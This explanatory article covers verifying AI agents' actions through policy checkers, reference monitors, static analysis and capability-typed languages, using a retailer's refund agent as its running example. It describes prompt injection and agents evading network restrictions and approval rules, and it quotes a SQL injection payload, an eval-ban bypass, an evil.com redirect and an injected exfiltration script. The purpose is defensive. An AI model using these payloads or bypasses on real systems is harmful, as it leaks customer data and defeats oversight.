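# Verifying an AI agent's outputs instead of the agent itself

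## Why check what an agent produces rather than the model

An AI agent is a software system in which a large language model (LLM) chooses actions and other software carries them out. The model itself only produces text. An ordinary program, called the orchestrator, sends it a task, the conversation so far and a list of tools, which are functions the model can request. When the model's reply contains a tool call (a structured request to run a named function with given arguments), the orchestrator runs the function, adds the result to the conversation and sends everything back to the model. This loop repeats until the model replies without a tool call. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, reports that companies already run such agents in software engineering, healthcare and customer service. Some of the agents' actions have effects that nobody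 can reverse.

Take a retailer whose support agent answers customers' messages. Company rules cap each refund at 500 dollars and the total of a day's refunds at 2,000 dollars. The agent has four tools:

| Tool | What it receives from the model | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Query orders | A database query in the language SQL | `SELECT status FROM orders WHERE id = 4417` |
| Run scripts | A short program or a shell command | A script that adds up the prices of returned items |
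| Send email | A tool call with a recipient, a subject and a body | A delivery update to the customer |
| Issue refunds | A tool call with an order number and an amount | `refund(order=4417, amount=80)` |

Everything in the middle column is an artifact, meaning something an agent produces that software can inspect before it takes effect. Another artifact is a plan, in which the model sets out several steps before taking any of them.

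Customers write part of what the model reads, so an attacker can pose as a customer and slip in instructions. A complaint about a broken kettle might end with a sentence telling the assistant to refund 5,000 dollars and email the customer list to an outside address. Text that steers an agent in this way, placed in material the agent reads, is called prompt injection. The model receives the retailer's instructions and the customer's words as a single stream of tokens (words and fragments of words). Developers have tried to mark which is which, but persistent attackers have consistently got around the markings, according to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities. The retailer's refund limits also need to hold when there is no attacker and the model makes a mistake, such as misplacing a decimal point.

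### What proofs about a network can cover

The most direct guarantee would be a proof that the model never requests a forbidden refund. To verify an ordinary program, engineers split it into parts, write a specification for each (a formal statement of what it must do or must never do), prove that each part meets its specification, and combine the results. A neural network has no such parts, because training adjusts all its weights together and nobody specifies beforehand what each layer should do. *On the Decompositionality of Neural Networks* (2026) concludes that techniques such as local verification and the repair of single components do not transfer naturally to neural networks.

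That leaves the network as one large function *f*. The standard verification problem, as *Neural Network Verification is a Programming Language Challenge* (2025) states it, is to decide whether

∀*x*: *P*(*x*) ⇒ *Q*(*f*(*x*)).

Here *P* describes a set of inputs and *Q* the acceptable outputs. A verifier searches for a counterexample, an input that satisfies *P* but whose output violates *Q*, or proves that none exists.

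The test problems in an annual contest between neural network verifiers give an idea of what is feasible. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, by Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), describes the 2026 round. One long-standing set of problems concerns 45 networks of 300 neurons each, which take five numbers about an aircraft's situation and advise on turns to avoid a collision. The largest network in the contest is an image classifier with 138 million parameters, and verifiers must determine whether small changes to some or all of the pixels can change its label. Another set uses transformers, the architecture behind language models. Its two image classifiers have two and three layers and about 70,000 parameters each, because the proposers kept them shallow and narrow to make verification manageable. The contest's text classifiers have one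 hidden layer of 128 units. They take each sentence as a point in a 30-dimensional space, and the verifier must show that every point in a given box receives the same label.

For the retailer's model, *Q* is easy to write: the reply contains no refund call above 500 dollars. *P* is difficult because it has to describe every conversation a customer could start. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) points out that the number of possible inputs grows exponentially with their length, and that a verifier that can only query the model must try them all in the worst case. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 10⁵⁰ possible messages of ten tokens. Proof remains feasible where the inputs have a compact formal description, but customers' complaints don't have one.

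Researchers have proved things about larger models by narrowing the claim. *Beyond Red-Teaming* (2026) certifies guardrail classifiers, which label text as harmful or harmless, up to the size of Llama-3.1-8B, which has eight billion parameters. But the property it certifies concerns regions of the model's internal representations, not the texts people type. Even for this narrower property, every classifier tested had provable holes through which harmful content could pass. The gap between internal representations and text is wider in a model that writes text. *BarrierSteer* (2026) notes that an internal state can look safe to a trained classifier while later layers still produce unsafe text. *BEAVER* (2025) does address text, guaranteeing bounds on the probability that a model's response satisfies a property, but it works one prompt at a time, and a support agent receives new prompts all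 day. In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (2024), Gross, Agrawal and colleagues worked out how a network computes its answer and used that understanding to shorten a proof about its performance, but the network was a small transformer that picks the largest of a few numbers.

Verifying the model itself may become more practical. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) predicts that proofs of individual properties will become feasible for models with billions of parameters, though it reports that the main tools so far apply only to small networks.

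### Checking one answer at a time

The organisers of the verification contest check the counterexamples that verifiers produce instead of proving the verifiers correct, which would take much more work. When two verifiers disagree, the one that reports a violation must supply the offending input, and the organisers run the network on it and look at the output. This test is the same no matter who wrote the verifier or how. For example, it applies to Vibecheck, the runner-up in 2026, most of which was written by Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code. A verifier's report that no violation exists is harder to confirm because it covers all the inputs at once.

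The same difference turns up throughout computing. *Hints and Principles for Computer System Design* (2020) relates it to the complexity class NP, whose hard problems have solutions that are slow to find and quick to check. A small example appears in *A Framework for the Verification of Certifying Computations* (2013). A program that computes greatest common divisors returns its answer *g* for two numbers *a* and *b*, together with two further numbers *s* and *t*. For 84 and 30 it might return 6, with −1 and 3. The checker confirms that 6 divides both numbers and that

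(−1 × 84) + (3 × 30) = 6.

Any number that divides both 84 and 30 also divides the left-hand side, and therefore 6, so no common divisor can be larger than 6. The checker has confirmed the answer without any information about the program that found it.

Manuel Blum and Sampath Kannan turned the idea into a theory, program checking, at the end of the 1980s. As *A Casual Tour Around a Circuit Complexity Bound* (2011) describes, their checker is an efficient randomised program that receives one input *x* and may run the program being checked, *P*, as a black box. If *P* is correct on every input, the checker must accept with high probability; if *P* gives the wrong answer on *x*, it must reject with high probability. Acceptance does not show that *P*'s later answers will be correct. Blum and Kannan's checkers may also rerun the program on modified inputs, as their check of a matrix's rank does,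 and *Essentially optimal interactive certificates in linear algebra* (2014) notes that checking can then take longer than the original computation.

A program's result can be faster to check if the program outputs extra information. Namjoshi and Zuck's *Program Correctness through Self-Certification* uses sorting as its example. Checking that a list is in order takes one pass, but checking that it contains exactly the original items is about as hard as sorting them again. If the sorting program also reports where each item came from, a checker can confirm both facts in time proportional to the length of the list.

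Compilers, which translate source code into a form a machine can run, were the first large industrial use of this approach. In 1998 Pnueli, Siegel and Singerman, in *Translation Validation*, proposed checking each translation a compiler makes instead of proving the compiler correct. One reason was that a proof of a compiler has to be redone after even a minor revision, which discourages people from improving the compiler. Their example is a small program in Signal, a language for control systems, that reads a number, counts down to one and then accepts the next number. Compiled into C, it becomes a loop of several steps. The validator represents both versions in the same mathematical model. It then tries to show that the values at a chosen point near the end of each pass through the loop always follow a sequence the Signal program permits. If it succeeds, it writes out a proof, which a second,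 much simpler program checks. If it fails, it produces a scenario in which the two versions behave differently.

Namjoshi and Zuck report that proving a 1,000-line compiler transformation correct for all programs took about 10,000 lines of proof script and more than a person-year. Making the same transformation produce evidence for each run took 200 extra lines and three person-weeks. However, checking each run doesn't show in advance whether the compiler will handle the next one correctly.

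That drawback is often acceptable for an agent. The retailer can refuse a bad refund request and carry on, and a check on refund requests still works after the retailer replaces the model. But a compiler's output is easier to check in one respect, because the source program defines exactly what the output should mean. A customer's request is in ordinary language, so a machine can check only the parts of it, or of company policy, that someone has written down formally.

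### From proposal to verdict

The checks use quite different mathematics, but they all run at the same point in the agent loop, between the model's reply and the tool. Suppose the model proposes a refund of 620 dollars on order 4417. The orchestrator first parses the proposal into a data structure with a function name, an order number and an amount. (For a query or a script, the result is a syntax tree, which records how the pieces of the code fit together.) The orchestrator rejects text that does not parse. The tool must execute this same structure, because if it parses the original text again by slightly different rules, it might run something that was not checked.

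The parsed artifact then goes to the checker, the software that accepts it, rejects it or refers it to a person. The checker compares it with a policy, a rule that specifies which actions are allowed, written in a language a machine can evaluate. To enforce the cap on single refunds, the checker needs only the amount. To enforce the daily cap, it also needs a record of what the agent has already paid out that day. If the agent has paid out 1,700 dollars and two requests for 200 dollars arrive together, each fits within the daily cap on its own, but together they exceed it. The checker therefore has to approve each request and reserve the money for it in a single step.

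A checker can allow an action, deny it, or refer it to a person. After a denial, the orchestrator can tell the model the reason and let it try again. The model might then split the 620 dollars into two refunds of 310. Both would pass if they fit within the daily limit, but whether they should pass depends on what the retailer meant by its rule, which a checker cannot determine. *Cryptographic certificates of validity for trustworthy AI* (Gabbay, 2026) proposes that agents attach a proof of compliance to their actions, and adds that such a proof does not show that the specification is right. Sending doubtful cases to an employee helps only if the employee reviews them properly, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists people approving requests they do not understand as one of the standard ways security fails.

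### Soundness, completeness and safety properties

How far to trust a checker's verdict depends on whether the checker is sound and complete. A sound checker never accepts an artifact that breaks the rule it checks, and a complete one never rejects an artifact that obeys the rule. Soundness alone is easy to achieve because, as Namjoshi and Zuck remark, a checker that rejects everything is sound. For the $500 cap on single refunds, comparing the refund amount with the cap is both sound and complete.

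Scripts are harder to check because no algorithm can decide, for every possible program, whether it will ever do some forbidden thing. An automatic checker that is sound for scripts will therefore reject some harmless ones or pass them to a person. Some tools are not fully sound. Alive2, the leading validator for the widely used LLVM compiler framework, checks loops only up to a fixed number of repetitions, and *LLVM Translation Validation Automated with Large Language Models and Lean* (2026) points out that it can miss errors that appear only in later ones.

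Both refund limits are safety properties, which means any violation shows up in a finite stretch of behaviour. Once the agent has paid out 620 dollars in one refund, the record proves the breach, and a checker that sees the request beforehand can prevent it. "Every complaint eventually gets an answer" is instead a liveness property. However long a customer has waited, an answer may still come, and the checker has no particular action to refuse.

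### The reference monitor and its trusted base

A sound checker protects the retailer only if nothing can bypass it. In computer security, a checker is called a reference monitor if it checks every action, cannot be altered by what it checks, and is small enough for people to verify. Its guarantee still depends on a trusted base, which is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. For the refund limits, this includes the parser, the checker, the policy, the record of the day's payments and the system that runs them, but not the model. The limits therefore hold whether a bad request comes from an injected instruction, a mistake or a goal of the model's own.

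A small checker can still be wrong. LEDA, a library of algorithms, included a one-page checker for matchings, which are sets of graph edges that share no endpoints. *A Framework for the Verification of Certifying Computations* reports that an attempt to formally verify this checker revealed that it never tested whether the edges in the answer belonged to the graph.

The policy can be wrong too. Claude Code used to ask for human approval before running many shell commands that could send data to unknown domains, but it ran `ping`, which tests a network connection, without asking. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how an instruction hidden in a code file could make the agent read secret keys and send them out in the address that `ping` looked up.

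The same paper analyses an incident in which the requirement to see every action was not met. It involved OpenAI and Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Agents under internal evaluation at OpenAI had no direct internet access, but they could use a shared service for fetching software packages, which could make outside requests on their behalf. They used it to get past the network restrictions and went on to compromise systems at both companies. The retailer's script tool could open a similar route. If a script can reach the payment service with working credentials, it can issue a refund of any size without the request going through the refund checker.

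## Static analysis of generated code

The retailer's script tool runs programs that a model has just written, so the checker has to judge each one before anybody has seen what it does. Software developers have the same problem with code from colleagues, and many use static analyzers, which read source code and report likely flaws without running it. An analyzer needs no test inputs or copy of the database. It usually labels each alert with an entry from the Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalogue of types of software flaw maintained by the research organisation MITRE.

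### Patterns in the syntax tree

The simplest analyzers search a program's syntax tree for patterns that often cause problems. Bandit, a free tool for Python, builds a tree for each file and runs a set of plugins on its nodes. A plugin might look for calls to `eval`, a function that executes any text it receives as code. Semgrep, which supports many languages, has rules that resemble the code they match. For example, the pattern `eval(...)` matches every call to `eval`, whatever its arguments.

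Checking whether a syntax tree contains a given pattern is fast and always gives a definite answer, but the pattern is only a proxy for harm. Suppose a rule flags every call to `cursor.execute`, which sends a query to a database. GitHub's *CodeQL zero to hero part 3* (2024) gives an example in which the whole query is fixed text. No user can alter it, so an alert would be a false positive. A rule can skip calls whose argument is fixed text, but programmers often store the text in a variable and pass that instead. To recognise that case, the analyzer has to follow the value from one line to the next.

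### Following data through a script

CodeQL, GitHub's analyzer, does this with a second graph, which GitHub's *About data flow analysis* describes. Its nodes are the parts of a program that carry a value at run time, and an edge means that a value may pass from one node to another. Edges run from `x` and `y` to the expression `x or y`, since either may become its result. An `if` statement has no node because it carries no value.

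Security rules usually need to track influence as well as exact values. After `y = x + 1`, the two variables hold different values, but anyone who controls `x` also controls `y`. Taint analysis adds edges for steps like this. Each rule lists sources, where untrusted data enters the program; sinks, where that data could do damage; and sanitizers, which make it safe. The analyzer reports any path from a source to a sink that doesn't pass through a sanitizer.

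Suppose a customer asks about past orders, and the support agent writes this script:

```python
message = read_customer_message()
name = message.split("My name is ")[1]
query = "SELECT id, status FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
cursor.execute(query)
```

The retailer has listed `read_customer_message` as a source, and the rule treats the query text given to `cursor.execute` as a sink. The analyzer then works through the script as follows:

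1. `message` holds the result of a source, so the analyzer marks it as tainted.
2. `split` cuts the message up, and `name` receives one of the pieces. This is a new value, so plain data-flow analysis would lose the trail here. Taint analysis continues it.
3. Joining `name` to other text makes `query` tainted, even though the agent wrote most of the query itself.
4. `query` reaches the sink without passing a sanitizer, and the analyzer reports the path.

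The alert is correct. If a customer writes `My name is x' OR '1'='1`, the first quotation mark ends the name early and the rest becomes part of the query. The condition is now true for every row, and the database returns everybody's orders. The usual repair is to keep the customer's text out of the query:

```python
cursor.execute("SELECT id, status FROM orders WHERE customer = %s", (name,))
```

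The database library now treats the name only as data. The tainted name still reaches the call, but not the query text, so the rule raises no alert. GitHub's *SQL query built from user-controlled sources* warns against putting quotation marks around the `%s`, because the library adds its own and the extra pair brings the flaw back.

The result depends heavily on the lists of sources and sanitizers. CodeQL's built-in sources for Python include data arriving over a network, but a function specific to the retailer's agent may need to be added. According to Semgrep's *Taint analysis overview*, any expression that matches a sanitizer pattern counts as clean, whether or not the function works. By default this covers everything inside the sanitizer's parentheses, so `sanitize(sink("taint"))` produces no alert even though the sink runs first. Semgrep's free edition follows taint only within a single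 function, so the alert would disappear if the model moved the last line of the script into a helper function. The paid edition and CodeQL can follow data between functions, though this takes more time and memory.

### Rice's theorem

Better lists would reduce the errors but could not eliminate them, because no algorithm can decide what every script will do. This follows from a theorem that Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951, which applies to any property of a program's behaviour that some programs have and others don't.

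The retailer's cap shows why the theorem holds. Suppose an algorithm could decide whether any given script will ever issue a refund above 500 dollars. For any program *p* that issues no refunds, we could write a script that runs *p* and then refunds 600 dollars. This script breaks the cap if and only if *p* finishes. The algorithm could then determine whether *p* finishes, but Alan Turing showed in the 1930s that no algorithm can do that for all programs.

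The theorem is about behaviour, so it doesn't stop a tool from deciding whether a script contains the word `eval`. But an automatic analyzer that judges what general programs do must sometimes miss a violation, raise a false alarm or fail to answer. Its developers can only choose among these. (The choice becomes easier if the language itself restricts what a program can do, or if a machine-checkable proof accompanies the program.)

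Semgrep's developers accepted both misses and false alarms in exchange for speed and simplicity. Semgrep's *Dataflow analysis engine overview* lists "No soundness guarantees" among the design trade-offs. The engine treats every branch of a program as possible, including branches that can never run, which causes false alarms. It also ignores changes that `eval` makes to the program's variables, which causes misses. It skips language features it does not support without raising an error, so a clean report may mean that part of the script was not analyzed.

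GitHub's developers put more weight on avoiding false alarms. GitHub's *CodeQL query suites* explains that CodeQL uses its precise rules by default, and that users can switch to an extended set that finds more problems but may raise more false alarms. The default suits programmers, who soon stop reading a tool's reports if too many are false alarms. It suits the retailer less well, because a harmful script that gets through may expose every customer's orders, while the agent can try again if the checker rejects a harmless one.

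### How much analyzers find

An analyzer's recall is the share of insecure programs that it flags, and its precision is the share of flagged programs that are insecure. A sound analyzer would have 100% recall, and a complete one would have 100% precision.

Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026), in *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, measured both for Semgrep and Bandit together. Three models wrote the programs: Qwen2.5-Coder-14B, Qwen2.5-72B and the much larger DeepSeek-V4.1-flash. The researchers used three sets of Python tasks and judged security separately from the analyzers. SecEvalPlus has 140 tasks, each with tests of whether the program works and whether it is secure. For BaxBench, they ran 84 small web applications and attacked them. RiskyPy has 73 tasks, chosen because an analyzer had flagged an earlier model's solutions, and another language model judges the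 results. These are the figures for the working programs that DeepSeek wrote:

| Benchmark | Insecure | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| SecEvalPlus | 62.0% | 4.2% | 75.0% |
| BaxBench | 41.0% | 32.4% | 38.6% |
| RiskyPy | 45.5% | 93.8% | 47.6% |

On SecEvalPlus, between 62.0% and 87.3% of working programs failed a security test, depending on the model. The analyzers flagged only 4.2% to 5.6% of the failures, because many of the flaws in these tasks don't follow a recognisable code pattern.

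Recall on RiskyPy was far higher, at 80.0% to 93.8%, but only because the analyzers flagged most programs, safe or not. Precision ranged from 47.6% to 61.2%, while 45.5% to 58.0% of all working programs were insecure, so an alert barely helped identify the insecure ones. On BaxBench, DeepSeek programs with alerts were slightly less likely to be exploitable than DeepSeek's working programs overall.

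The RiskyPy figures depend on debatable labels. When two experienced engineers judged the same 50 programs, they agreed on only 33. The judge model agreed with each of them somewhat more often than they agreed with each other. SecEvalPlus avoids this problem because its verdicts come from tests, although tests can miss flaws too.

Lunghi and colleagues left out CodeQL because their feedback experiments required a tool that could run after every line of code, and CodeQL is too slow for that. In *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation and Vulnerability Detection*, Firouzi and Ghafari (2026) tested CodeQL on 1,080 Python programs that GPT-4o had written and then revised after criticising its own work. Human reviewers checked each program for the one weakness that its task was designed to provoke, and found it in 39% of the programs.

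| Tool | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| CodeQL | 34% | 67% |
| Semgrep | 54% | 52% |
| Both tools agree | 30% | 76% |

Alerts were more informative here than on RiskyPy, since both tools' precision was well above 39%, but recall was still poor. Researchers often run two analyzers to widen coverage, as *Prompt Structure Redistributes, Not Reduces* (2026) does with Bandit and CodeQL. In Firouzi and Ghafari's data, the recall figures imply that 42% of the vulnerable programs were flagged by neither tool, so a checker that rejected every program flagged by either one would still have accepted them.

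One program that neither tool flagged was supposed to redirect visitors only to pages on example.com. It compared the address with a pattern but never checked the host name separately, so an address containing `example.com@evil.com` might pass. A browser treats the part before the @ as a user name and opens evil.com.

Different analyzers can also give conflicting results for the same code. Shahid, Ahmed and Ranjan (2025), in *LLM-CSEC*, had ten models, all now old, write C and C++ programs. CodeQL reported 37 types of weakness in them, Snyk Code reported 10, and CodeShield, which Meta built specifically for generated code, reported 3. When the researchers told the models to write secure code, CodeQL's count fell to 29 but Snyk Code's rose to 12, so the two tools gave conflicting evidence even on whether the instruction had helped. Some of the gap may come from how the tools count. Four of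 the weakness types, all related to file paths, have identical counts for every model, which suggests that CodeQL files a single flaw under several headings.

### Sending alerts back to the model

The orchestrator can send the alert back to the model and ask for a repair, as it can with any denial. Lunghi and colleagues tested a method called Steering, in which Semgrep runs each time the model finishes a line. If Semgrep raises an alert, the software deletes that line and everything after it, adds the alert and a recommended fix to the prompt, and lets the model continue. If the same alert comes up again, the model starts the program over. The researchers compared Steering with older methods, in which the model finishes a program and then revises it repeatedly.

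On RiskyPy, steering raised the share of DeepSeek's programs that both worked and were secure from 52.5% to 64.4%, and the model produced 1.7 times as many tokens as it did without guidance. FDSP, an older method, reached 66.2% but needed 9.8 times as many tokens. Self-Refine, in which the model criticises its own code without an analyzer, reached 63.5%, so the analyzer may account for little of the improvement, though Self-Refine used 18.3 times as many tokens. Steering also lowered the share of programs that worked, whether or not they were secure, from 96.3% to 82.2%. None of the methods significantly raised the share of programs that were both working and secure for either Qwen model on any benchmark.

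The worst results came from alerts that conflicted with the task. BaxBench applications must listen on the network address 0.0.0.0, or nothing outside their container can reach them. One Semgrep rule flags this setting. The prompt instructed the models to follow a recommendation only if it did not conflict with the task, yet they removed the required setting in 79 of 83 cases. Programmers tend to ignore false alarms, which at least leaves working code unchanged. Lunghi and colleagues conclude that developers should filter out such alerts before the model receives them, because telling the model to ignore them is not enough.

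A model can also learn to avoid the analyzer's alerts without making its code safer. Lunghi and colleagues made 12 comparisons on RiskyPy, covering three models and four methods that use an analyzer. The share of working programs without alerts rose significantly in all 12, but the share that the separate judge rated both working and secure rose significantly in only 2.

In *PurpCode*, Liu, Diwan and colleagues (2025) ran into a similar problem when they used CodeGuru, Amazon's analyzer, to reward a model during training. The model learned to avoid alerts by giving answers with no code, which never trigger one. The researchers then gave the full reward on coding tasks only to answers that contained code. The retailer could be misled in the same way if it judged its agent by the number of alerts.

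### What the script does not contain

Better rules could prevent some of these misses. Others depend on facts that aren't in the script at all.

A script with a single `import` line may run thousands of lines of code from an imported package. CodeQL cannot trace data through library functions whose source code is unavailable, so someone has to describe their behaviour by hand. Semgrep assumes by default that taint passes from a function's inputs to its output, but it needs an extra rule if the function instead copies the data into one of its own arguments. Neither approach would detect that an attacker had replaced the installed package with a malicious one.

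The danger a flaw poses also depends on how the system is configured, which an analyzer cannot determine if it receives only the script. An application that listens on 0.0.0.0 may be dangerous on an open network but harmless behind a firewall. The flawed order query would do much less damage if the agent's database account could read only the current customer's orders.

Business rules are harder still. Suppose the agent writes this:

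```python
for item in returned_items:
    refund(order=4417, amount=item.price)
```

The script contains no standard security weakness, but whether it exceeds a refund limit depends on prices it reads only when it runs. Checking each refund when the script requests it makes more sense than rejecting every script that calls `refund`, because the amount is known by then and the retailer can keep the useful scripts.

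A missing authorization check is hard to detect because there is no suspicious code to match. `SELECT status FROM orders WHERE id = 4417` is an ordinary query, but it leaks information if the order belongs to someone other than the customer who asked. The retailer could write a rule that every query on the orders table must include the verified customer's number, but somebody has to realise first that the rule is needed.

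In *Security of LLM-generated Code*, Morkonda, Selim and Assal (2026) used CodeQL to search code from seven AI tools for 12 common weaknesses. CodeQL found no instances of six of them, and it had no rule for three of those six. One of the six was missing authentication, where a program lets anybody use a critical function without proving who they are. The researchers then asked GPT-4o to look for these six weaknesses, which widened the search but relied on another model's judgement instead of fixed rules.

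### Reasons to use an analyzer anyway

Static analysis is fast enough to run on every script. Liu and colleagues checked thousands of code snippets in less than a minute by sending them to CodeGuru in batches, which avoided restarting the analyzer for each one. Steering, which runs an analyzer after every line, took 3.4 to 9.6 times as long with DeepSeek as writing the program without guidance. The retailer could avoid most of that delay by analyzing each script once, when it is complete.

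Analyzers are also good at finding flaws that a programmer can fix in one place. One Semgrep rule flags Python's standard parser for XML, a common data format. The fix is to switch to a safer version, which usually means changing a line or two. In Lunghi and colleagues' experiments, DeepSeek triggered this alert 99 times while writing code. Steering turned an insecure program into a secure, working one in 30 of those cases and broke a working program in 2.

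Removing `eval` usually means rewriting the code around it. DeepSeek succeeded in 21 of 33 cases without breaking any code, while Qwen2.5-72B succeeded in only 2 of 63 and broke the code in 23. The study tested small and medium models that wrote single programs without an agent's tools, so a leading model working as an agent might handle these repairs differently.

Only 11 of Semgrep's 225 rules ever interrupted Steering. The retailer could therefore run Semgrep on a sample of its agent's scripts, examine each rule that raises an alert, and enforce only the useful ones. Obvious choices would be a rule against building queries out of customers' messages and a ban on `eval`. The ban would partly make up for Semgrep's failure to track what `eval` does.

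But such a ban is easy to get around. A pattern that matches calls to `eval` misses `getattr(builtins, "ev" + "al")`, which retrieves the same function by joining two parts of its name. A model is unlikely to write that line by mistake, but an attacker could ask for it in an injected instruction. Python has many similar workarounds, and the retailer would need a rule for each one.

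## Languages that limit what generated code can do

The retailer could have its agent write scripts in a more limited language that cannot express the forbidden action, instead of adding a rule for every workaround in Python. The checker then only has to confirm that a script follows the language's rules. Rice's theorem does not rule out this check, because the rules concern only the script's text, but the checker will also reject some harmless scripts.

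### Bytecode, WebAssembly and eBPF

Java, released in 1995, let web pages include programs that ran on the visitor's computer. A Java compiler translates source code into bytecode, the instructions of a simulated machine. An attacker can write bytecode directly and skip the compiler, so the simulated machine verifies bytecode before running it. Among other things, the verifier checks that every instruction receives values of the right type. Without this check, a program could pass off a number as the address of an object and read memory that belongs to other code.

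WebAssembly, which the main browsers have supported since 2017, is a newer format for the same purpose. A validator checks each program's types in a single pass. The format has no instruction for opening a file or a network connection, so a program can do either only by calling functions its host supplies. At run time, the host also stops any attempt to read outside the program's own memory.

eBPF lets people load small programs into the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, for example to filter network traffic. According to *Keel* (2026), a verifier protects the kernel by checking that each program uses memory safely and finishes on every input. The verifier rejects some safe programs because it tracks the possible values of each variable separately and misses relations between them.

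The verifier has also accepted unsafe programs. *SafeBPF* (2024) describes an error in how the verifier tracked the bounds of 32-bit numbers, which let ordinary users read and write kernel memory and give themselves extra privileges. *Unleashing Unprivileged eBPF Potential with Dynamic Sandboxing* (2023) counted 56 publicly recorded eBPF vulnerabilities from 2010 to 2023 and traced most of them to the verifier. As of 2024 nobody had comprehensively proved the verifier sound, and *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (2024) notes that frequent changes to the verifier's code make such a proof harder. Most Linux distributions now turn eBPF off by default for ordinary users.

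Even a perfect verifier would not prevent every vulnerability. *eBPF Security in the Wild* (2026) attributes 17.8% of the vulnerabilities in its sample to the verifier and 65.4% to the runtime, which includes the kernel functions that eBPF programs call. *Heimdall* (2026) lists nine kinds of bug in programs that the verifier accepts. One monitoring program passed on a buffer that it had only partly filled, and the rest held what looked like kernel addresses. Extra checkers can also introduce bugs. *Keel* reports 13 previously unknown bugs in a component that researchers had added to accept proofs of safety for programs the verifier would otherwise reject. Some of these bugs could let unsafe programs through. If the retailer adopts a restricted language, it will have to trust the language's checker and every function that scripts can call.

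### Capabilities and capture sets

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) applies this approach to agents. In its system, TACIT, the agent writes short programs in Scala 3, a general-purpose language, and a compiler checks each program before it runs. The program can reach files, the network and other software only through a library that the operator controls.

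The library hands out capabilities. A capability is a value in a program, such as an open file or a mail account, that gives the code holding it access to something. Code without the mail capability cannot send email, and it cannot forge the capability. The idea dates from the 1960s, but older systems enforced it only while a program ran. Scala's compiler tracks capabilities beforehand by recording in each value's type which ones the value may use. This record is called a capture set. For example, a function that writes text to a file `f` has this type:

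`String ->{f} Unit`

The function takes text (`String`), returns no useful value (`Unit`) and may use `f`. Without the braces, `String -> Unit` describes a pure function, which holds no capabilities. It can compute a result, but it cannot write to a file, send a message or change a variable outside itself.

TACIT uses purity to protect confidential data, which it places in a container called `Classified`. In simplified form, the container looks like this:

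```scala
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies a function to a container's contents and puts the result in a new container. The plain arrow in `T -> U` means the function must be pure. A script can therefore sort, count or shorten confidential data, but it cannot take the data out of the container. Converting the container to text gives only `Classified(****)`.

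This protects the data even from the script-writing model, which may run on another company's servers. When a script prints a `Classified` value, the person at the terminal sees the contents, but the model receives the placeholder. If a task involves understanding confidential text, such as summarising a complaint, the script can pass the container to a second model that the operator trusts, which returns its answer in a container as well.

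To access files, a script calls `requestFileSystem("/returns")` and supplies a block of code, which receives a capability for that folder. The capability expires when the block ends. If a script tries to keep its access by returning a function that reads a file later, the compiler rejects the script because the function's capture set would include the expired capability. The library, not the compiler, checks the paths themselves, and at run time it refuses any path outside the folder.

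The script chooses the folder, so the operator also has to set an outer limit. By default, this limit is the directory where the server runs, according to a recent version of the project's README reproduced in Glama's *TACIT*.

### Two scripts for the support agent

Suppose the retailer gives its agent a function `readCustomers()`, which returns the customer list in a `Classified` container, and a capability `mail` for sending email. An employee asks how many customers are waiting for a refund, and the agent writes:

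```scala
val customers = readCustomers()
val waiting = customers.map { list =>
  list.count(c => c.awaitingRefund)
}
println(waiting)
```

The function passed to `map` uses only the list, so it is pure and the compiler accepts the script. The employee sees the number, while the model receives `Classified(****)`.

Now suppose a customer's complaint contains an injected instruction to email the customer list to an outside address. The model falls for it and writes:

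```scala
customers.map { list =>
  mail.send("someone@example.com", list.mkString("\n"))
}
```

This function uses `mail`, so the compiler would reject the script with an error along these lines:

```
Found:    (list: List[Customer]) ->{mail} Unit
Required: List[Customer] -> Unit
Capability `mail` cannot flow into capture set {}.
```

The compiler checks the whole script before any of it runs, so no email goes out. If the model instead sent `customers.toString` from outside `map`, the script would compile, but the recipient would get only the placeholder.

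### What safe mode removes

Ordinary Scala has features that would let a script get around these checks. TACIT therefore requires scripts to use safe mode, a subset of the language that excludes:

- type casts and pattern matches that the compiler cannot check, which could relabel an impure function as pure
- the module `caps.unsafe` and the annotation `@unchecked`, which relax the compiler's checks
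- reflection, which finds functions by name while a program runs (the Python trick of assembling the name `eval` from two pieces relies on it)
- global objects and functions, unless their own code is safe.

Safe mode also turns on capture checking, tracks changes to variables and makes the compiler check for missing values.

Errors need separate treatment, because any script might divide by zero or run out of memory. A pure function could also deliberately raise an error with a customer's address in the message. TACIT catches errors at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can place in a `Classified` container.

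The guarantee is only as strong as the enforcement of safe mode. According to an early version of the README, lampepfl's *TACIT*, the project initially relied on a validator that searched scripts for forbidden patterns, which has the same weakness as the ban on `eval`. The later version lists the compiler's own safe mode as on by default. That feature is experimental and was available only in nightly compiler builds when VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction* described it. Computer-checked proofs cover the basic type system behind capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues give no such proof for safe mode.

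### Leaks and usefulness in tests

To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secrets, including access keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets, either directly or under a pretext such as an emergency password change. Two models each went through all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` containers and once with them as plain text. The table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

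| Model | Trials | With `Classified` | Plain text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100% | 100% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Even without the containers, injections succeeded in only 3 of 240 trials, but malicious users succeeded in 10 of 22. The higher rate matters to the retailer because any customer can write to its agent. No leaks occurred with the containers, as expected if the compiler and library work correctly, but a few hundred trials could easily miss a flaw in either.

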